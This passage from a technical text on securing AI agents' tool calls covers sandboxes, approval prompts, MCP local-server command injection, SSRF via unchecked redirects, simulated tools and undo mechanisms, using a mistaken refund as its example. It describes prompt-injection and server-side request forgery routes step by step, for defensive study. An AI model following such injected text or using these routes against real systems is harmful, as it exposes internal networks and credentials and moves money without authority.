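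If the shop's staff approve 200 refunds a day, they may well approve the 2,000-euro refund too, even if the prompt describes it clearly. The shop could ask for approval only when a refund exceeds the order's price, but a program that can detect this can also refuse the payment without asking. Staff approval is more useful when the records are not enough to decide, such as whether to compensate a customer who is frustrated after receiving three broken lamps.

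## Sandboxes, simulated tools and undoing a call

The host, the guard model and the person at the approval prompt can all let a harmful call through. The damage then depends on what the code can reach and whether anyone can reverse its effects. A sandbox limits which files, networks and processes the code can reach. But a single refund can involve code running in three places, and each place needs its own isolation.

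| Place | Example | Who can isolate it | What isolation protects |
|---|---|---|---|
| The agent's code | The loop that refunds broken lamps | The host's operator | Files, keys and networks on the host's machine |
| The tool server | The exchange-rate server | The host's operator if it runs locally, otherwise its owner | The machine and network that the server runs on |
| The remote service | The payment processor | Its owner | The service's own systems |

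A container around the agent's program does not restrict a tool server that the host started outside the container. Neither the host nor the shop can put the payment processor in a sandbox, because it belongs to another company and moves money whenever it receives a valid request.

### What each method blocks

TACIT uses its programming language's types to limit what code can do. The methods below work from outside the program, so they do not depend on a compiler being able to analyze it.

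A restricted interpreter runs part of a programming language and gives the program only the functions the host supplies. A container gives a program its own view of files and processes but shares the kernel, the central part of the operating system, with the rest of the machine. A virtual machine has its own kernel, so a program that takes over that kernel still has to break through the layer separating it from the real machine. A network allowlist names the addresses a program may connect to.

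| Method | Blocks | Leaves open | Main cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Restricted interpreter | Files, networks and commands that the host has not exposed | Harmful use of the exposed functions | Many ordinary libraries do not run |
| Container | Files and processes outside the container | Attacks on the shared kernel, and usually the network | Developers have to build and update the container |
| Virtual machine | The same, plus most attacks on the real machine's kernel | Usually the network | More memory and a slower start |
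| Network allowlist | Connections to unlisted addresses | Harmful requests to listed addresses | New tools fail until someone lists their addresses |

Start-up time is a small part of a sandbox's overhead. In a 2026 comparison by Pydantic, which develops the Monty interpreter, Monty started in 0.06 milliseconds, a Docker container in 195 milliseconds and a commercial sandbox service in about a second. Even a second matters little to an agent that waits several seconds for each reply from its model. The libraries missing from an interpreter are more likely to make a developer choose a container instead.

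Operating systems can also restrict an ordinary program without a container. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) describes such a sandbox for Claude Code. Commands, and any programs they start, can change files only in the current project directory. All internet traffic passes through a proxy, a program outside the sandbox that checks each domain against a list and asks the user about new ones.

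A sandbox's restrictions on file access and network access depend on each other. An agent with unrestricted network access could send out any secret file it can read, and an agent that can change any file could alter the sandbox's settings to open the network.

In Anthropic's internal use, the sandbox reduced permission prompts by 84%, because commands inside it no longer needed approval. This figure measures convenience, and the post doesn't give the number of attacks the sandbox stopped. The post's claim that even a successful prompt injection is "fully isolated" is overstated, because a manipulated agent can still damage the project it is working on and send data to any listed domain that accepts uploads.

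A sandbox also has to be set up correctly. In July 2026, Anthropic disclosed that misconfigured test environments had let its models reach real organizations' systems.

### The refund uses a permitted connection

Suppose the shop runs the agent's program in a virtual machine that can connect only to the shop's tool server. The program calls `issue_refund("A-1043", 2000)`. The call goes through because it uses the same permitted connection as every legitimate refund, and the payment processor pays out 2,000 euros. Deleting the virtual machine afterwards does not reverse the payment.

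Removing the tool server from the sandbox's allowlist would block the incorrect refund, but it would also block every other refund. The sandbox can't block only the incorrect one, because the allowlist filters by address and the error is in the amount. The sandbox would still stop the agent from sending the shop's payment key to a stranger's server.

A proxy can do more if it reads the requests. In the web version of Claude Code, the agent's sandbox never contains the user's login details for git, the system that stores versions of code. A proxy outside the sandbox checks what the agent is trying to upload and where before adding the login. The shop could keep its payment key in a similar proxy, which would compare each refund with the order before adding the key. This would stop the 2,000-euro refund on a 20-euro order, but the comparison would be a contract of the kind described earlier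 and would also depend on knowing the unit. The sandbox would ensure that no payment could bypass this check.

### Starting a local server runs its code

Many MCP servers run on the user's own machine. The host starts them with a command from a configuration file:

```json
{ "command": "python", "args": ["exchange_rates.py"] }
```

The host then exchanges messages with the new process through its standard input and output (STDIO). The host cannot request the tool list until the server is running, so all the checks on descriptions, schemas and calls begin after the server's code has started. That code usually has the same access to files as the host.

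OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains* (April 2026) examines what happens when someone else can fill in the command meant to start an MCP server. MCP's official libraries run whatever command they are given and report an error only afterwards if it did not start a server. The security company found web applications that passed users' text straight into the command field, so a visitor could run commands on the application's server.

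The settings page of Letta, a platform for building agents, offered only remote servers, but Letta's backend still accepted local ones. The researchers altered the request after it left the browser and ran a command on Letta's machines. LangFlow, another tool for building agents, gave every visitor a session token without requiring a login, and the researchers counted 915 copies of LangFlow on the public internet.

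OX Security's *Anthropic design choice Exposes 150M+ Downloads and up to 200K Servers* reports that the team ran commands on six live platforms. The "200K" in its title is an upper estimate of vulnerable installations, not a count of tested machines. A machine with the library is vulnerable only if an outsider can influence the command.

Anthropic did not accept the finding as a vulnerability. According to ITPro's *AI agents using Anthropic MCP could be a vector for supply chain*, it replied that the attack "requires explicit user permission for the file change". The reply seems to refer to coding assistants, where an attacker's text can lead the agent to add a server to the configuration file. OX Security's *MCP Supply Chain Advisory* reports that most of the assistants tested asked the user at least once before making such a change, though the user might not know what the new entry contained.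 One assistant, Windsurf, changed the file and ran the command without asking.

The reply does not apply to the web applications, where the attacker enters the command and the application's owner is never asked. For the libraries themselves, Anthropic instead called the behaviour expected and held developers responsible for checking the input.

There is a good argument for that position. A function whose purpose is to start a program has to run a command, and Python's standard library has functions that do the same. The Model Context Protocol security policy states that a malicious local server "already has arbitrary code execution by virtue of being run", and that the STDIO connection is not a sandbox. SecurityWeek's *'By Design' Flaw in MCP Could Enable Widespread AI Supply Chain Attacks* also says it is fair to hold developers responsible for what they build, and notes that GitHub's installation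 withstood OX Security's tests.

But so many developers made the same mistake that a safer default could have prevented much of the harm. OX Security proposed letting users choose only from complete commands set up beforehand by the developer, or making developers switch on a setting marked as unsafe. It also suggested a list of permitted programs, though its own tests show that this protection is weak. Its researchers got past such a list in Flowise, one of the affected products, because one of the permitted programs could run other commands passed to it as arguments.

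Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* requires hosts that install local servers with one click to show the full command and wait for approval. It also recommends running the server in a sandbox with few privileges. Approval alone gives weak protection, since `python exchange_rates.py` looks the same whether the file fetches exchange rates or copies the user's keys.

A sandbox would only partly limit what that file could do. Some vendors rejected OX Security's reports because their products ran the commands in Docker containers. OX Security agreed that this protected other users' data, but pointed out that an attacker could still use the machines to mine cryptocurrency or to hide the origin of other attacks.

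### Redirects to internal addresses

A harmless tool server can also make a harmful connection. Google's MCP Toolbox connects agents to databases and web services. One of its tools sends web requests to an address that the developer sets, with the caller supplying the path at the end. Google's original advisory, published in a public vulnerability catalogue as MITRE's *Server-Side Request Forgery via Unrestricted HTTP Redirection in MCP Toolbox* (2026), describes how a caller could reach other addresses.

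The tool did check the caller's input, but its HTTP client followed redirects without checking where they led. A redirect is a reply that tells the client to fetch a different address. Suppose the shop has set the tool to contact only `partner.example`:

1. Text in an order leads the agent to request a path on `partner.example` that forwards visitors to any address named in the link.
2. The Toolbox sends the request, because the domain is the permitted one.
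3. The partner's server replies with a redirect to `10.0.0.5`, an address inside the shop's network.
4. The Toolbox follows the redirect and may return the internal page to the agent.

This attack is called server-side request forgery, and malicious schema references also make it possible. On many cloud platforms, a request to one of these internal addresses returns login details for the company's cloud account.

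The fault affected versions 0.3.0 to 1.4.0. Google rated its severity at 8.0 out of 10, and the record lists no known attacks using it. OSV's *CVE-2026-16481* (2026) describes a related fault, published four days earlier, in which another Toolbox tool fetched an address supplied by the caller without validating it and could expose credentials.

A sandbox around the agent's code would not have helped, since the request came from the tool server. The server has to check each address itself, including every address that it receives in a redirect:

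```
fetch(url):
    repeat at most 5 times:
        reject if the domain is not on the allowlist
        ip = look up the domain's numeric address
        reject if ip is private or local
        reply = connect to ip, without following redirects
        if reply is not a redirect: return reply
        url = the address in the redirect
    reject
```

The client connects to the numeric address it has just checked instead of looking up the domain again. Otherwise, an attacker who controls the domain could return a public address for the check and an internal one for the connection. Model Context Protocol's guidance recommends these precautions for hosts that fetch login information, and they also apply here. It also advises developers not to write their own address checks, because an address can be written in several ways and home-made checks often miss some of them.

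Banning all private addresses would be too strict for a database tool, since a company's databases are usually on its internal network. According to the Russian-language article *ИИ-агенты могут передавать друг другу вредоносные команды через MCP*, Google's fix blocks unsafe addresses and adds lists of permitted address ranges. A developer can then allow access to one database without exposing the rest of the network. A separate proxy that enforces the same rules would protect the company even if the tool's own check failed.

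### Letting a model play the tool

Developers can avoid real effects by testing the agent on simulated tools, but writing a realistic imitation of each tool takes a lot of work. ToolEmu (Ruan, Dong and colleagues, 2023) instead used a language model to simulate the tools. The model received a tool's specification, the agent's call and the earlier calls, and wrote a plausible result. In a second mode, it looked for circumstances in which the agent was likely to cause harm. Another model then read the whole run and judged how likely and severe the possible damage was.

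ToolEmu has 144 test cases for 36 toolkits. According to its automatic judge, even the safest agent failed in 23.9% of cases. ToolEmu was a quick way to find problems worth investigating, but human reviewers judged that only 68.8% of the failures it reported could happen with real tools. The agents in the study are now long out of date.

A model that invents tool results can produce ones that contradict the real environment. *A Context-Aware LLM-Based Action Safety Evaluator for Automation Agents* (Lin and Milani Fard, 2025) gives the example of an agent that should find and stop the five programs using the most processor time. ToolEmu returns made-up programs with random identification numbers. The simulation contains no information about what the real programs are, so it can't show whether stopping them would be safe.

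Their own system, an adaptation of ToolEmu, runs part of the task for real:

1. The agent proposes an action, and a model decides whether it only reads.
2. If it does, the system executes it on the user's machine and records the result.
3. At the first action that might change something, the system switches to simulation and gives the simulator the results collected so far.
4. A model describes the possible risks, and another judges the run.

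For the refund, this system would look up the real order and find that it cost 20 euros. It would then simulate the payment.

The paper's reported experiments do not test whether the real results help, although its abstract claims that experiments show a benefit. The reported experiments measure how well a model judges 162 recorded runs from an existing benchmark. GPT-3.5 was right in 54.9% of cases without a description of the risks, 75.3% with the benchmark's description, and 73.5% with one that GPT-4 wrote. The part of the software that writes descriptions could not yet use results from the machine, and Lin and Milani Fard leave that test to future work.

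The design also relies on a model to recognize actions that only read. If the model mistakes a deletion for a read, the system deletes the files during the safety check itself. The paper assumes that the agent has full administrator rights, which would make such a mistake worse. Even a correctly identified read can expose a password to the models that process the result.

### Invented behaviour for an unfamiliar tool

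A simulator has more to go on when it plays a well-known command than when it plays a tool that nobody has seen before. Its training data contains countless examples of how the command for listing files behaves. For `issue_refund`, it has only the description and the schema, neither of which gives the unit. When the agent sends 2000, the simulator has to guess, and it may well return:

```
Refunded 20.00 euros on order A-1043
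```

The developer would conclude that the agent handles refunds correctly, and the real tool would then pay out 2,000 euros. The simulator made the same assumption as the agent because it had the same information. If it had happened to assume euros, the test would have exposed the error.

False descriptions cause the same problem. The PDF converter described as working "locally" would do so in a simulation, because nothing in its description would cause the simulator to simulate an upload. Simulation can therefore test what an agent does if a tool's description is true, but not whether the description is true.

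If ten simulations of the same call produced refunds of both 20 and 2,000 euros, this would show that the tool's description leaves something important open. The developer could then ask the tool's owner about it before connecting the agent. Ten matching results would be weak evidence of safety, because models tend to make the same guess about what the description leaves out.

### Comparing the records before and after a run

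A working copy of a service gives better evidence than a model's account of one. Pysklo, Zhuravel and Watson (2026), in *Agent-Diff*, built copies of four services that companies use for messages, files, project management and calendars. The agent writes code that sends requests to what appear to be the real services, and the test environment redirects the requests to the copies. Each copy stores its data in database tables, which the system saves before and after the run. It then computes three sets:

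```
added    = records present only after the run
deleted  = records present only before the run
changed  = records with the same key but different content
```

Each task comes with a list of expected changes and a list of fields to ignore, such as the time of the last update. Any other change counts as a side effect and reduces the score to zero, however many of the expected changes the agent made. The order of the calls does not matter, so an agent can solve the task in a way that the task's author did not foresee.

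If the shop built a copy of its own system, a test of the refund might produce this:

```
expected   refunds:   1 record added, order A-1043, 20 euros
ignored    orders:    time of last update

found      refunds:   1 record added, order A-1043, 2000 euros
           customers: 1 record changed, locked: false -> true
```

The comparison shows that the amount is wrong and that an account was locked, an effect missing from the tool's description. Unlike a contract, the comparison needs no condition on the customer's account, because the system reports every change that the task does not explain.

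Pysklo and colleagues tested nine models on 224 tasks, three times each, without giving them documentation for the services. Scores out of 100 ranged from 38.0 for Llama 4 Scout to 88.1 for DeepSeek V3.2. Relevant documentation raised the average share of fully solved tasks by 7 percentage points. The scores combine unfinished work with side effects, so they do not measure how often the agents changed something they should have left alone.

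The method finds only the effects that the copy records. The copies leave out notifications, on the grounds that the agent cannot observe them and they do not affect the evaluation, but notifications can matter a great deal in a safety test. If an agent creates a calendar event and deletes it a second later, the tables show no difference, but the real service might have emailed fifty people.

Someone also has to build the copy. Pysklo and colleagues built their copies from public documentation and checked them against the real services. If the documentation for a refund tool does not state the unit, a developer working from it would have to guess, as the simulating model did. The shop could find the unit in its own code, but it could not read the code of a stranger's exchange-rate server. An agent that finds a tool halfway through a task has no time to build and check a copy.

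A host with access to the records can also compare them on a live system. It would detect the 2,000-euro refund only after the payment, and would have to separate the agent's changes from those other people made at the same time. Still, the shop is more likely to be able to reverse an error found within seconds than one found at the end of the month.

### Undo and damage confinement

In 2024, Patil, Zhang and colleagues presented GoEX, a runtime in which an agent acts first and the user then checks the result and either keeps or undoes it. They reasoned that people can judge the result of an action more easily than a block of code or a proposed call.

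GoEX undoes changes to files by restoring earlier versions that it has kept. For databases, it can group changes into a transaction, which the database discards unless somebody confirms it. For web services, it has a language model write a second call that reverses the first, such as one that deletes a message the agent has just posted.

For actions that cannot be undone, GoEX relies on damage confinement, which restricts the agent's permissions beforehand so that the worst outcome stays within a limit the user accepts. For example, an agent that may only read emails cannot send any. The paper mainly describes a design, so it provides little evidence on how often reversals would work in practice.

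A reversal written by a model can repeat the mistake it is meant to correct. Suppose the agent has refunded 2,000 euros by calling `issue_refund("A-1043", 2000)`, and the shop's `charge_customer` tool takes amounts in cents. The obvious reversal is `charge_customer("A-1043", 2000)`, which recovers only 20 euros and leaves the shop with a loss of 1,980 euros.

Later systems borrow more from databases. *SagaLLM* (Chang and Geng, 2025) uses the saga, an old method for long transactions. Each step in a plan has a compensating step, and if a later step fails, the system runs the compensating steps for the completed steps in reverse order. If it had booked a flight and then a hotel, it might cancel the hotel and then the flight. *STRATUS* (Chen, Pan and colleagues, 2025) applies undo to agents that repair cloud systems. If a repair leaves the system worse than before, the agents undo it and try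 another. This requires a reliable measure of "worse", and cloud operators often have one in their alerts and error rates. The shop would need its own measure, such as a comparison of each refund with the order.

### Reversible, compensable and irreversible calls

Whether a call can be undone affects how much checking it needs beforehand.

| Type | What can happen afterwards | Example | Sensible treatment |
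|---|---|---|---|
| Reversible | The earlier state returns completely | Renaming a file, or a database change not yet confirmed | Execute it, keep the old state and show the result |
| Compensable | A new action offsets the effect, at a cost or with some risk of failure | Booking a hotel that charges for cancellation | Execute it within a limit and prepare the offsetting action |
| Irreversible | Nothing restores the earlier state | Emailing a secret to a stranger | Check or ask first |

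A refund is compensable at best. The shop can ask for the money back or charge the card again, but the customer may refuse, the card may have expired, and the original payment stays in the accounts. Compensation works much better for honest mistakes than for theft, because a dishonest customer who planted the false claim about cents will probably have moved the money out of the account by the time anyone notices.

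MCP's hints do not distinguish reversible calls from irreversible ones. Sending an email counts as an addition, not a destructive change, though no one can take it back. The server could offer a cancellation tool, but the tool's name would not prove that it restores everything. A host should therefore treat calls to an unfamiliar tool as irreversible until somebody has tested the reversal.

A call can also change type over time. A payment order is reversible while it waits in a queue but only compensable once the money has moved. The shop can therefore hold every refund for an hour before sending it to the payment processor. During that hour, a program can compare the refunds with the orders, an employee can look at the unusual ones, and the shop can cancel a refund by deleting a record in its own database. Customers wait an hour longer for money that often takes days to arrive. The delay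 would be harder to justify for an agent that reserves the last seat on a flight, since someone else may take the seat within the hour.
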